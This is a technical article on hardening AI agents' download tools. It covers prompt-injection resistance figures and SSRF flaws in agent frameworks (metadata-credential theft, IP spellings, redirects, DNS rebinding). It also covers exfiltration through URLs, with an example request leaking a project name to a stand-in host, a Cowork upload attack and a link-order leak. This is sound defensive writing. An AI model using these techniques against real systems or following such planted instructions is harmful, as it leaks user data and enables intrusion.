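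Repeated attempts matter because an attacker can plant many reviews or pages. If each attempt succeeded independently with probability $p$, the chance of at least one success in $k$ attempts would be

$$P_k = 1 - (1 - p)^k$$

The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports how the November 2025 model performed on a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan. A single strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time, and the rate rose to 33.6% within ten attempts and 63% within a hundred. If every attempt had the same independent chance of success, those rates would be 38% and 99%. The lower observed rates suggest that the failures were concentrated in some scenarios, while others withstood repeated attacks. The average can therefore understate the risk for a developer whose application resembles one of the weak scenarios.

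Models have improved quickly since then. Schneier (2026), in *Anthropic’s Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection*, quotes a success rate for indirect attacks on Claude Opus 5 of 0.2% for one attempt and 2.0% within fifteen. Within fifteen attempts, the rate was 16.5% for Muse Spark, the best model from another company, and 20.0% for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports 8.5% within fifteen attempts for Astra, on 1,810 attacks that Gray Swan selected. The two sets of results can't be combined into one ranking, because GPT-5.6 Sol scored 27.0% on that test and 20.0% in the comparison with Opus 5. *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a review of a later Anthropic system card, reports further improvement against indirect injection.

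OpenAI attributes much of its progress to training against an automated attacker called GPT-Red. According to The Hacker News (2026), GPT-Red sends a prompt, observes the response and keeps adjusting until it reaches a malicious goal, such as uploading sensitive data to an outside server. OpenAI called its previous models "highly vulnerable" to these attacks. In its internal tests, resistance to indirect attacks rose from 96.23% with GPT-5.6 Sol to 99.79% with Astra.

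Text the agent reads remains a bigger problem for these models than text the user types. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed about 0.05% of the time against direct attacks and 3.77% against indirect ones. In TicketOracle, direct attacks worked on five models and a planted review on only two, but the first version had no instruction about which URLs to refuse. OpenAI counts an attack as direct when a user tries to override higher-priority instructions. Once TicketOracle's system prompt included an instruction about which URLs to refuse, every direct attack failed.

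### Whether tools check what they receive

If an attacker's URL gets past the model, the tool's code can still reject it. Ananto and colleagues built ToFu to find out whether tools do this. ToFu uses fuzzing, which tests software by running it on many automatically altered inputs.

Ordinary fuzzers look for crashes, but a tool that fetches a forbidden address usually finishes normally. To recognise this failure, a tester has to know what the tool was supposed to refuse. ToFu derives this from the description the tool already gives the model. If an argument is described as a "file within the workspace", the tool should refuse paths outside the workspace, and if an argument is a web address, the tool should restrict the scheme and destination.

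ToFu comes with a library of 74 checks, which the researchers call sanitizers. Each has four parts:

$$S = \langle A, G, O, I \rangle$$

$A$ describes the arguments the check applies to, $G$ the hostile inputs to try, $O$ the rule the tool must follow, and $I$ what to observe while the tool runs. The language model GPT-4.1 reads the tool's description and picks the relevant checks. For many checks, it also decides whether the tool should reject a bad input, return a harmless fallback or accept the input. The option to accept matters for tools whose purpose is to run code. ToFu ran one such tool, which executes AppleScript, more than 2,000 times without raising an alert.

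The model also writes about eleven starting inputs per tool, and the fuzzer then varies them for 60 seconds. Ordinary code decides whether a rule was broken, so the model has no part in that judgement. For tools written in Python, ToFu records which files they open and which addresses they contact. For other tools it mostly relies on the response, and reports a violation for input $x$ to tool $T$ when

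$$V(x) \land \neg \mathrm{Reject}(T(x), E)$$

Here $V(x)$ means that the input breaks the rule, and $E$ is any evidence of side effects. The formula means that the tool should have refused the input but didn't.

The researchers started from a catalogue of 13,875 MCP records. They kept Python and JavaScript projects with at least ten stars on GitHub, and the final set was the 273 servers on which at least one tool call succeeded. The paper gives several totals for what ToFu found:

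| Count | What it refers to |
|---|---|
| 508 | Candidate bugs before review |
| 253 | Verified bugs, after the researchers removed 103 false alarms and 152 duplicates |
| 343 | Tools that the 253 bugs affect, since one bug can affect several tools |
| 118 | Servers that contain those tools |
| 436 | Candidates from a single run of a later experiment, which nobody reviewed by hand |

There are therefore 253 distinct flaws. Dividing 343 by the 3,405 tools on all the servers suggests that about one tool in ten is flawed, but the true share is probably higher because many tools needed a login or a missing service and never ran. Only about 1,500 ran in the later experiment.

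Most of the bugs have little to do with downloads. In 115 cases a tool returned dangerous input without neutralising it, and in 58 an attacker could forge log entries. The most important for download_file are the 64 path traversal bugs, which let a caller read or write files outside the intended folder, and the 7 cases of server-side request forgery (SSRF).

Seven is a minimum, because the researchers found five more SSRF bugs on one WordPress server when they applied all 74 checks to every tool. ToFu had missed them because GPT-4.1 chose a check that works only on Python programs, and the server was written in JavaScript. Running every check on every tool isn't practical, though, since more than 90% of the reports on newly flagged tools were false.

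### The screenshot tool that opened local files

One of the tools, on a server called webpage-screenshot-mcp, takes a URL and returns a picture of the page. The argument's description is "The URL of the webpage to screenshot." The code checks only that the value is a valid URL, then passes it to a browser.

GPT-4.1 matched the argument to eight checks, including one that permits only http and https, and specified that the tool should return an error if any check failed. The starting inputs included loopback addresses and a `file:` URL, which points to a file on the computer's disk. The server rejected inputs that weren't URLs, but when it received the `file:` URL, it returned an image of the file and a message that the screenshot had succeeded.

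The researchers repeated the call by hand and found that the tool would display any file the server's account could read. When given a folder, it returned a picture of the contents. It also applied saved login cookies by default, so an injected instruction might be able to capture pages that require the user's account. Only the word "webpage" in the tool's description ruled out local files, and no code enforced that restriction. The `https` pattern in the stricter download_file schema would have blocked the `file:` URL.

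### Better models or checks in code

The case for relying on better models is stronger than it was a year ago. Attacks once succeeded a third of the time within ten attempts. On the best model in Anthropic's comparison, they now succeed 2% of the time within fifteen attempts, although the two figures may come from different benchmarks. A good model can also use context that a URL check lacks. If an employee asks for a summary of a report and the agent starts sending payroll figures to a file-sharing site, the address may be acceptable, and the model can recognize the request as wrong only from the conversation.

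But if Opus 5's failure rate of 0.2% per attempt held outside the benchmark, a planted page that 10,000 agents read would still succeed about 20 times. Developers also switch models, often to cheaper ones, and TicketOracle shows how much can change when only the model is different. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that Opus 5 alone failed in 3.7% of browser tests. It reached 0% only with Anthropic's Auto Mode, which scans incoming content for hidden instructions and blocks dangerous actions before they run.

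A check in code gives the same result whichever model made the call and however persuasive the planted text was. The TicketOracle attacks all targeted services on the server itself, so a working address check in fetch_event_data would have stopped them even with Llama. The check would have had to allow the application's legitimate event pages, which were also on a private address. A password on the administrative interface would also have helped.

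Developers often leave the checks out of code, as the 253 bugs show. Even so, fixed rules, such as never contacting an internal service, belong in code, and the model's judgement is most useful for requests those rules allow.

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian would go further and not let the model supply a URL at all. In TicketOracle, the model could name a concert and the application could build the address from its own list. That is the safest design when the destinations are known in advance. A general download tool has to accept links that no developer has seen, so its code must work out where each one leads before connecting.

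## Blocking downloads from internal addresses

In server-side request forgery (SSRF), an attacker who can't reach an internal service gives the service's URL to a server that can, and the server makes the request. Many internal services don't require a password because their owners rely on the network to block outsiders, as with the administrative interface in TicketOracle.

Building a download tool that refuses internal addresses, the obvious defence, is harder than it sounds. The developers of PraisonAI, a Python framework for running teams of agents, fixed SSRF flaws in six separate releases during 2026. Each flaw came from a different wrong assumption about how a URL becomes a connection.

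### Where internal addresses lead

An IPv4 address is a 32-bit number, usually written as four numbers from 0 to 255. Internet standards reserve some ranges of addresses for use inside one machine or one network, and IPv6, the newer standard, has similar ranges of 128-bit addresses. The number after the slash in a range such as 10.0.0.0/8 is how many leading bits its addresses share, so this range contains every address that starts with 10.

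| Kind | IPv4 | IPv6 | What a request reaches |
|---|---|---|---|
| Loopback | 127.0.0.0/8 | ::1 | The machine that sends the request |
| Private | 10.0.0.0/8, 172.16.0.0/12, 192.168.0.0/16 | fc00::/7 | Other machines on the organisation's network |
| Link-local | 169.254.0.0/16 | fe80::/10 | The immediate network link and, on most clouds, the metadata service |
| Shared | 100.64.0.0/10 | None | Equipment inside a provider's network |

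The cloud metadata service is usually the most valuable target. It gives programs on a cloud machine credentials for other cloud services, such as file storage, so that developers don't have to store passwords on the machine. Amazon, Google and Microsoft all put it at 169.254.169.254.

The older version of Amazon's service returns a machine's credentials in response to ordinary GET requests. OSV's *GHSA-8f4v-xfm9-3244* (2026), an entry in a public database of flaws in open-source software, shows that stealing them takes two requests. The first returns the name of the machine's role. The second, with that name added to the address, returns an access key, a secret key and a token. Anyone who has these credentials can use the machine's cloud permissions until the credentials expire.

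A download tool can write credentials from an internal address to a file and return only a success message. This makes them harder for a monitor to notice than if the tool had returned them in the conversation. The file may also outlast the conversation, and a later step in the agent's work could upload it.

### PraisonAI's download_file

PraisonAI's agent package, praisonaiagents, has a tool called download_file(url, destination). According to OSV's *GHSA-44c2-3rw4-5gvh*, published on 1 April 2026, the tool checked the destination but passed the URL directly to an HTTP client that followed redirects. AutoGPT's developers had made the same choice three years earlier. Version 1.5.95 of praisonaiagents fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-34954.

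To demonstrate the flaw, a tester started a small web server on the loopback address and called download_file with its URL. The server logged the request. The tester did not report trying a real metadata service, but the code did not treat a metadata service's address differently. The tester also turned on PraisonAI's automatic approval setting, so a person might have the chance to stop the call in installations where that setting is off.

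The advisory suggested a fix, which works like this (with shorter names and messages):

```python
BLOCKED = [ip_network(n) for n in (
    "10.0.0.0/8", "172.16.0.0/12", "192.168.0.0/16",
    "127.0.0.0/8", "169.254.0.0/16")]

def check(url):
    parts = urlparse(url)
    if parts.scheme not in ("http", "https"):
        raise ValueError("scheme refused")
    try:
        address = ip_address(parts.hostname)
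        if any(address in block for block in BLOCKED):
            raise ValueError("address refused")
    except ValueError as error:
        if "does not appear to be" not in str(error):
            raise
```

The function stops a download by raising an error. If it finishes without one, the download goes ahead. Here is what it does with a private IPv4 address, the IPv6 loopback address and a hostname:

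| Host in the URL | What `ip_address` does | What follows | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| `10.0.0.5` | Returns an IPv4 address | The address is in 10.0.0.0/8, so the function raises "address refused" | Blocked |
| `::1` | Returns an IPv6 address | All five blocked ranges are IPv4, and Python never counts an IPv6 address as part of an IPv4 range | Passes |
| `intranet.example` | Raises an error, because the text "does not appear to be" an IP address | The last two lines recognise that message and discard the error | Passes |

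Adding IPv6 ranges to the list would fix the second case. The third is more serious. The last two lines let hostnames through because without them the tool would reject most legitimate links. But the function doesn't resolve the hostname to an IP address, so even `localhost` passes. It also doesn't check redirects.

OSV's *PYSEC-2026-3535* (2026) reports that the file containing PraisonAI's download_file later looked up each hostname and checked every address returned. Other projects still leave this step out by default. Vercel's AI SDK, a toolkit for building AI applications, automatically checks URLs that outside model providers return, but it checks only the text of the URL and any IP address written in it. Developers have to turn on DNS protection themselves.

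### The same flaw in PraisonAI's other tools

The better check stayed in one file, and researchers kept finding SSRF flaws in the package's other web tools: web_crawl, which fetches pages, and the spider tools, which extract text and links. The table follows the order of the fixed releases, but its dates are those of the public notices, some of which came out long after the fix.

| Notice in 2026 | Tool | False assumption | Fixed in praisonaiagents |
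|---|---|---|---|
| 1 April | download_file | Only the destination needs a check | 1.5.95 |
| 10 April | web_crawl | Any URL is safe to fetch | 1.5.128 |
| 6 May | Spider tools | The check and the HTTP client read a URL in the same way | 1.6.32 |
| 29 May | Spider tools | An internal address has only one spelling | 1.6.40 |
| 18 June | Spider tools | A hostname can't lead to an internal address | 1.6.58 |
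| 5 August | web_crawl | The client will fetch only the URL that passed the check | 1.6.58 |
| 15 July | web_crawl | A hostname still leads to the same address when the client connects | 1.6.78 |
| 11 July | web_crawl with a browser | A check before the browser starts covers the browser's own connections | 1.6.78 |

Until version 1.5.128, web_crawl accepted any address. If the HTTP library httpx was missing, the tool used a Python module that also opens `file:` URLs, so it could read local files. A fresh installation used the unchecked httpx path by default, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-40160* (2026). The fix added a check on the initial URL, which left the redirect and rebinding flaws in place.

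The spider tools did check the URL, using one library to extract the host, but then passed the original text to a second library, which extracted the host again. OSV's *GHSA-q9pw-vmhh-384g* (2026) describes how a misplaced backslash made the libraries disagree, so the tools checked a public address but connected to the loopback address. As with tool calls, the remedy is to parse once and use that result for both the check and the connection.

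**Alternative spellings.** The check compared the host with a few exact strings, such as `localhost` and `127.0.0.1`. But the address $a.b.c.d$ stands for the number

$$N = 2^{24}a + 2^{16}b + 2^{8}c + d$$

and many programs accept that number directly. They would treat 3221225985 as 192.0.2.1, an address that standards reserve for documentation. They may also accept hexadecimal and octal forms, and forms with fewer than four parts. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2902* (2026) lists five variants of the loopback address, including `localhost` with a dot at the end, that all passed the check and reached a test server. Version 1.6.40 added code to recognise more numeric forms.

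The new code still checked only the text of the host, without looking up the address it resolved to. A domain's owner can point it at any address, including an internal one, so an attacker could get past the check with an ordinary DNS record. The attacker did not even need to own a domain, because some public DNS services resolve a hostname containing an IP address to that address.

The researcher who reported this replaced Python's lookup function with one that raises an error when called, then ran PraisonAI's check on a hostname. The check finished without an error, so it never performed a lookup. A reviewer could easily have missed this, because the check was documented as blocking hostnames that resolve to internal targets.

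SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55526* reports that the developers had already added a hostname lookup to web_crawl but never copied it to the spider tools. OSV's *CVE-2026-55526* (2026) gives 1.6.58 as the fixed version, while the earlier OSV entry gives 1.6.59. OSV says the fix calls Python's `getaddrinfo`, which can return all of a host's IPv4 and IPv6 addresses, but SecureLayer7 says it calls `gethostbyname`, which returns a single IPv4 address and would miss an internal IPv6 address for the same hostname.

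web_crawl checked only the first URL, and its HTTP client then followed redirects automatically. An attacker's public server could therefore pass the check and redirect the client to the metadata service. Rapid7 reports that this affected versions 1.5.128 through 1.6.57 and describes it as an incomplete fix of the April flaws. According to SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55525*, version 1.6.58 turned off automatic redirects and checked each new target before following it.

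### DNS rebinding

A tool that looks up the hostname and checks every redirect can still connect to an internal address. The check performs one DNS lookup, and an ordinary HTTP client performs another when it connects. In an attack called DNS rebinding, the attacker runs the domain's name server and changes the answer between the two lookups. The attacker gives the first answer a very short lifetime so that the second lookup doesn't reuse it from a cache.

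```
Download tool                          Attacker's name server
-------------                          ----------------------
CHECK
Where is files.example?  ----------->
                         <-----------  A public address,

valid for 1 second
Public address: allowed

Changes the record

to 127.0.0.1
CONNECTION
Where is files.example?  ----------->
                         <-----------  127.0.0.1
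Connects to its own machine
```

The URL is identical in both steps, so examining its text more carefully wouldn't help. Checking the address again just before connecting would shorten the gap but not close it. The solution is to pin the address, which means connecting to the one that passed the check without another lookup. If the attacker changes the record after the check, the change then has no effect on the connection.

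It is unclear which version of PraisonAI first pinned the address in web_crawl. SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55524* says version 1.6.58 did. But OffSeq's *CVE-2026-61430* (2026) and VulnCheck's *PraisonAI before 1.6.78 DNS Rebinding SSRF via web_crawl* say that versions before 1.6.78 still looked up the hostname again at connection time. Operators should therefore treat 1.6.78 as the first version with this fix. As of late November, OffSeq had no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw outside tests.

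### A check that covers the connection

A sound check has to control the connection as well as examine the URL. In order, the tool should:

1. Parse the URL once, and build the request from the parsed parts.
2. Refuse every scheme except http and https.
3. Look up all of the host's IPv4 and IPv6 addresses, and refuse the URL if the lookup fails.
4. Refuse the URL unless every one of those addresses is public.
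5. Connect to one of the addresses it has just checked, while keeping the original hostname for the HTTP request and for TLS, the encryption that https uses.
6. Keep automatic redirects off. If the server sends a redirect, return to step 1 with the new URL, and give up after a fixed number of redirects.

Another PraisonAI flaw shows why a failed lookup in step 3 has to block the download. The framework can send a notice to a web address when a job finishes, and it checked that address before sending. OSV's *CVE-2026-55537* (2026) reports that the check accepted the address if the lookup failed, and that PraisonAI looked up the address again when it sent the notice. An attacker's name server could therefore ignore the first query and answer the second with an internal address.

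In step 4, it is safer to define what is public than to list everything that is internal, because a list can leave something out. Python's standard `ipaddress` module can do most of this:

```python
def is_public(ip):
    return (ip.is_global
            and not ip.is_multicast
            and not ip.is_reserved
            and not getattr(ip, "is_site_local", False))
```

The last condition covers fec0::/10, an old IPv6 range for internal networks. OSV found that Python's tests for private and reserved addresses miss this range. The conditions can still miss some internal services, because a company may run them on public addresses behind a firewall that lets its own servers through. No general test of address ranges can recognise those addresses as internal.

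The tool should reject a hostname unless every address it resolves to is public, even though the tool will connect to only one. A mix of public and internal addresses is suspicious in itself, and an HTTP client may try the next address if the first connection fails.

Step 5 needs the hostname for two reasons. One server often hosts many websites and uses the name in the request to choose between them. With https, the server must also present a certificate for that name, and a certificate for files.example will not normally match a bare IP address. If a developer avoids the resulting error by turning off certificate checks, anyone who can intercept the connection can replace the file.

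HTTP libraries offer different ways to pin an address. *SSRF Protection*, a page in the documentation of the PHP framework Nette, describes giving the curl library the hostname together with its checked addresses, so that curl connects to one of those addresses and the URL stays unchanged. Alternatively, the code can put the address in the URL and supply the hostname separately.

A tool can also be stricter than step 2 and accept only https. The protected fetcher in FastMCP, a framework for building MCP servers, does this and also checks and pins addresses. A rebinding attack would then work only if the internal service had a valid certificate for the attacker's hostname, which is unlikely. The tool would also refuse the metadata addresses in these advisories, which all use plain http, as long as it applied the same rule to redirects. However, it couldn't download files from some older sites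 that still offer them only over http.

### Pydantic AI's fix

Pydantic AI, another Python framework for agents, had a similar flaw, which OSV's *CVE-2026-25580* (2026) made public on 6 February. It affected applications that accept chat history from users. An attacker could send a message with a file attachment whose URL pointed to an internal address, and the framework would download the file for some file types and model providers. The attacker did not have to get the model to call a tool.

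Version 1.56.0 fixed this. According to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2980* (2026), it accepts only http and https and blocks loopback, private, link-local and shared addresses by default. It also blocks the IPv6 range for 6to4, an older way of carrying IPv4 traffic inside IPv6 addresses. A developer who needs files from an internal server can set an option called `allow-local`. Even with that option set, the framework was meant to block three metadata addresses: 169.254.169.254, Amazon's IPv6 equivalent and Alibaba Cloud's 100.100.100.200.

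Pydantic AI protects against DNS rebinding by pinning the address, according to its source code, which Glama hosts in its directory of MCP servers. It checks every address the hostname lookup returns, puts the first one into the URL, and sends the original hostname in the HTTP header. For https, it also uses that hostname to check the certificate. It handles redirects itself, repeats the whole check for each one, and stops with an error at the eleventh. The advisory attributes the protection to looking up the hostname before the request, but a lookup alone wouldn't be enough, since PraisonAI's web_crawl did that too.

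This closely matches the steps above. The main difference is in step 4, where Pydantic AI started from a list of blocked ranges and had to extend it twice. The code compared each address as text with the three metadata addresses. Some IPv6 addresses contain an IPv4 address, and certain networks deliver traffic for the IPv6 address to that IPv4 address. A metadata address embedded this way didn't match, and the `allow-local` option had switched off the other check that might have caught it.

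OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2978* (2026) describes the first repair, in version 1.99.0, which covered three ways of embedding an address. OSV's *CVE-2026-48782* (2026) describes the second, in version 1.102.0, which covered more. The flaws these repairs fixed were much narrower than the original one, because they could be exploited only if the developer had allowed local addresses for a URL that an attacker could influence. The second flaw also required an unusual network setup, and a standard cloud machine would not have been affected in practice. Some networks choose their own prefix for embedded addresses, so no fixed list of ranges can cover every case.

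For projects that couldn't upgrade to 1.56.0 immediately, the advisory published a filter that removes suspicious file links from the chat history. It refuses a link when the lookup fails, and the lookup converts alternative spellings into ordinary addresses before the check. It is much weaker than the fix in other ways:

- **Rebinding.** The filter performs one lookup, and the download performs another later.
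- **IPv6.** It uses `gethostbyname`, so it never sees a hostname's IPv6 addresses.
- **Redirects.** It checks only the link in the message, so it can't stop a redirect that the download follows.
- **Alibaba Cloud.** It relies on Python's `is_private`, which is false for the shared range 100.64.0.0/10. Alibaba's metadata address is in that range and passes.

The filter may also remove nothing, because it looks for file links among the top-level parts of each message, while Pydantic AI normally stores them one level down, inside the content of the user's prompt. A developer who has to stay on an old version should test the filter with a harmless link before relying on it. Removing all user-supplied file links would be safer.

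### Browsers and other programs

Address checks work only if the tool controls the connection. Many agents use a headless browser, which a program controls without opening a window, because some pages show their content only after running scripts. The browser handles DNS lookups and redirects itself.

PraisonAI's web_crawl used a browser in this way when the optional crawl4ai package was installed. It automatically chose crawl4ai, which opened pages in Chromium. According to a researcher's account reproduced in OffSeq's *CVE-2026-61429* (2026), PraisonAI checked the first URL and passed it to Chromium, which connected without further checks. In a test network, the researcher used both DNS rebinding and a redirect to retrieve a planted secret from an internal server.

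The researcher recommended restricting the browser to the checked address or allowing it to visit only approved sites. The first option is difficult with ordinary web pages. Checking a page's own address doesn't cover the images, scripts and frames it can load from dozens of other hosts, or anything its scripts request after it opens.

The same problem arises when a tool starts another program to do the download, such as curl, git or a package installer. The tool can give curl a pinned address and leave redirects off, but many programs have no such options. Some also make requests that don't pass through the tool. A package installer also fetches the package's dependencies, and a video converter may open addresses listed in its input file.

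If a tool passes a hostname to a proxy, the proxy looks up the address, so the proxy has to check that the address isn't internal. FastMCP has a separate mode for trusting a proxy. In that mode, it refuses the request if no configured proxy will handle it.

In all these cases, the tool can check the first URL and reject obvious attacks, but egress rules have to block the connections the tool can't control.

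## Deciding which public addresses an agent may fetch from

The checks in the previous section keep a download tool away from internal machines, but they allow every public server, including one an attacker has just set up. Such a server can return a harmful file. It can also collect data from the request itself, so an agent can leak a secret even if nobody opens the file.

### How a download request carries data out

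Suppose the employee's agent has read internal notes about a project with the code name Bluebird. It then opens a supplier's web page, where an attacker has hidden an instruction to fetch a brochure and include the project's name in the address. If the model complies, it calls download_file with a URL like this:

```
https://files.example.net/brochure.pdf?project=bluebird
```

The server receives the path and the query string, and most web servers write both to a log. The server may answer with a real brochure, an empty file or an error. Even if the tool deletes whatever arrives, the attacker can still read "bluebird" in the log. Encryption doesn't help, because the attacker's server decrypts the request.

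The name could also go into the hostname, as in `bluebird.files.example.net`. To connect, the tool has to look up that hostname, and the query normally reaches a name server that the domain's owner controls. The address check in the previous section includes this lookup, so the check could leak the name even if it then refused the download. The tool therefore has to apply any rules about hostnames before the lookup.

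A read-only fetch tool can still leak data. In *The Read-Only Lie*, the blogger dyb points out that a GET request can't write anything, but its path still carries information to the server. Some developers have still treated fetching as harmless. *Takedown* (2025), a study of attacks on coding agents, describes one agent whose built-in fetch tool ran without the user's approval. By default, that agent had the contents of the user's open files in its context.

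Data may leak without a tool call. The security firm PromptArmor describes how this can happen when an agent talks to its users through a messaging app such as Slack or Telegram. If an attacker gets the agent to write a link with private data in it, the app may fetch the link to show a preview, which sends the data out even if nobody clicks. Checks inside download_file can't stop this, so the application also has to check the links in the agent's replies or turn previews off.

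One countermeasure is to search outgoing URLs for secrets. Lan and colleagues tried a filter for words such as "password" and another for random-looking strings, and no data left in 30 runs with either. Without defences, they recorded attempts to send data in every run, compared with only 23% of runs with the word filter and none with the other. These results are hard to interpret, because a filter that acts after the model has written its call shouldn't change what the model writes. They also tested pages that told the agent to send a key in four-character pieces, one per request. The filter for random strings ignored values of ten characters or fewer, so it would have missed those pieces. Neither filter would catch a secret that is an ordinary word, such as "bluebird".

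### Domain allowlists

An allowlist names the hosts a tool may contact, and the tool blocks requests to all others. An attacker's server that isn't on the list can't supply a file or receive a request.

Lan and colleagues compared an allowlist with defences that rely on the model, using a page that told the agent to send out a secret:

| Defence | Runs in which data left, out of 30 |
|---|---|
| None | 30 |
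| Tags that mark web text as untrusted | 30 |
| A system prompt that forbids following instructions from web pages | 20 |
| Both the tags and the system prompt | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 0 |

With the allowlist in place, the model still tried to send the secret in all 30 runs, and the code blocked every attempt. This was an easy test for an allowlist because the attacker's domain was clearly not on it.

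**Matching the host.** The code that compares a host with the list is short and easy to get wrong. In *Your Agent May Misevolve* (2025), a study of agents that build their own tools, a user asked an agent for a function that checks whether a URL belongs to a given domain. The agent wrote a function that tested whether the host ended with the domain's name. It later reused the function on a list of URLs that included a malicious look-alike, which passed. The table shows how that test compares with two safer ones when the list contains `example.com`:

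| Host | Ends with `example.com` | Equals `example.com` | Equals it, or ends with `.example.com` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `example.com` | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |
| `docs.example.com` | Accepted | Refused | Accepted |
| `notexample.com` | Accepted | Refused | Refused |

Anyone can register a name like the one in the last row. The same study tested eight models on 25 pairs of tasks and found unsafe tool creation or reuse in 65.5% of cases on average. That figure covers many kinds of flaws in models from 2025, so it doesn't show how often a current model would get a domain check wrong. It is still a good reason not to let an agent write its own allowlist code.

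Exact matching is the safest default. Accepting subdomains is convenient, but it means trusting whoever controls each one. An attacker can sometimes claim a forgotten subdomain that points to an outside hosting service. According to Anthropic's documentation, the domain filter in its web fetch tool includes subdomains automatically, so an entry for `example.com` also covers `docs.example.com`. It also warns about names that look identical but use letters from another alphabet, and recommends writing the list in ASCII characters.

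Matching the hostname correctly gives little protection if an attacker can publish on an allowed site. Code repositories, file-sharing services and cloud storage often put thousands of customers under one hostname, so allowing that hostname allows files from all of them. Some of these services also let customers see who requested their files. Where the service gives each customer a separate path, the rule should include the path. Some allowed sites also have pages that redirect visitors to any address given in the link, so the tool has to check every redirect against the list.

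Anthropic ran into the problem of shared services with Claude Cowork, an agent for office work. Cowork's network rules allowed only certain domains, including Anthropic's own API, which Cowork needs to run. According to the software developer Simon Willison (2026), PromptArmor showed in January how to get files out through that domain. A malicious document contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key, and Claude used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The network rules allowed the upload because it went to an approved domain.

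Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* concludes that an allowlist entry is better understood as a "capability grant", because it permits everything the domain can do. Anthropic fixed the flaw with a proxy that accepts only the session's own credentials. A download tool is less exposed if it sends only GET requests and attaches no credentials supplied by the model. However, some services change data in response to GET requests, as TicketOracle's administrative interface did.

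The main drawback of an allowlist is that somebody has to know the sites in advance. This is practical for an agent that collects invoices from ten suppliers, but an agent that researches unfamiliar subjects would repeatedly have requests refused. Enforcing the list at the network as well extends it to browsers and other programs the tool starts.

### Rules about where a URL came from

For the second kind of agent, a developer can allow any site but restrict where the URL comes from. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the documentation for a tool that reads pages and PDFs, describes such a rule. Claude could fetch a URL only if it had already appeared in a user's message, in the result of a tool that the developer's application ran, or in an earlier search or fetch result. The tool refused URLs that Claude made up and URLs from the environment where Claude runs code.

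If $K$ is the set of URLs from permitted sources, the tool fetches a URL $u$ only when

$$u \in K$$

In the Bluebird example, the attacker doesn't know the project's name and so can't write the finished URL on the page. The attacker can only include instructions for building it, and the URL that the model builds isn't in $K$. Ordinary code checks this, so the rule holds even if the attacker fully deceives the model. The tool also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters, which limits how much data a single request can carry.

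The set $K$ is only as trustworthy as its sources. Willison (2025) noted when the tool came out that many applications paste emails or web pages into the user's message, and the rule then treats the links in them as the user's own. Results from the developer's tools can also contain hostile text. A developer who applies this rule to download_file should record which links the person typed and keep that record on the server, where nobody can forge it through the chat history.

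A page's author can still get information from an agent that fetches only URLs in $K$, by listing many complete URLs and seeing which ones the agent picks. Ayush Paul published an attack of this kind on 9 July 2026. Paul built a website whose pages offered Claude sets of links, one for each letter, and gave it a reason to spell out its user's details by following them. Every link was in $K$ because it had appeared in a page that Claude had already fetched. Claude didn't insert a secret into any URL, but the order of the requests in the server's log spelled out the details. Willison (2026) reports that Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer, which Claude knew from its memory of past conversations.

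If an agent makes $m$ choices in a row from $n$ links, it can reveal up to

$$m \log_2 n$$

bits of information. Eight choices from 26 links give about 38 bits, enough to spell any eight-letter word. A limit on the number of fetches would reduce $m$, but a short secret needs only a few requests.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. It then stopped the tool from following links found inside pages it had fetched. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* gives the same account. The fix removes the easiest way for an attacker to offer the agent a long series of choices, but it makes the tool less useful for downloads, because the link to a report is often on a landing page. The user may have to paste the direct link, or the agent may have to find it through a search. Search results can still contain several pages from one attacker's site, so the agent's choice between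 them could still leak a smaller amount of information.

### Checking that a URL is already public

According to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), ChatGPT can automatically fetch a URL that exactly matches one in an index of public URLs. OpenAI builds the index with a crawler that has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If there is no match, the system tells the agent to try another site or warns the user that the link may contain information from the conversation.

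Nothing would lead the crawler to record the brochure URL ending in `project=bluebird`, so the agent couldn't fetch it without the user noticing. The check applies to the whole URL because a reputable domain can redirect to a hostile one. It also covers images, which an application may load in the background.

Johann Rehberger, who writes the security blog Embrace The Red, reported the underlying leak to OpenAI in early 2023, years before this check arrived, and found ways around OpenAI's first fix, from December of that year. His post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* calls the new check a significant improvement but describes a remaining leak much like Paul's. An established website may already have 36 pages in the index, enough for one per letter and digit, and hidden instructions could tell the model which page stands for which character. Rehberger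 suggests that the agent should not request the same URL twice in a session, or should reuse a stored copy. The attacker could then no longer reuse a page for a repeated letter, but could still assign a page to each of many common words on a site with thousands of indexed pages.

For a download tool, the larger drawback is that many legitimate files are not public. The employee's report might be behind a personal link in an email or have gone online an hour ago. Some websites ask OpenAI not to catalogue them, and OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links* explains that users then have to confirm every link to those sites. OpenAI's guarantee covers only data leaks through the URL, and a file at a well-known public address can still be malicious.

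### What a person can usefully approve

When the allowlist and the URL rules leave a request undecided, the usual fallback is to ask the user. To decide on a download, the user needs to know which host will supply the file, its size and type, and where the tool will save it. But before contacting the server, the tool has only the original URL and the save location. The server declares the size and type in its response, and a redirect may change the host. Requesting these details before asking the user would send the server the URL, including any private data in it.

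The tool can solve this by pausing at two points. Before any lookup or connection, it shows something like this:

```
Download a file from files.example.net?

Full address:   https://files.example.net/brochure.pdf?project=bluebird
Data it sends:  project = bluebird
Save in:        reports
```

After approval, the tool sends the request but doesn't yet accept the file. If the server redirects to another host, the tool shows the new address and asks again before following it. When the final server responds, the tool compares the declared size and type with fixed limits and asks only if something is unusual. It should present the size and type as the server's claims, because the actual file may differ.

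The line about the data matters most for preventing leaks. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* describes a system that detects when a link would pass on information from the conversation, then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation or blocks the request. A user who sees "bluebird" next to an unfamiliar host has a reason to refuse that "Allow download_file?" alone wouldn't give them.

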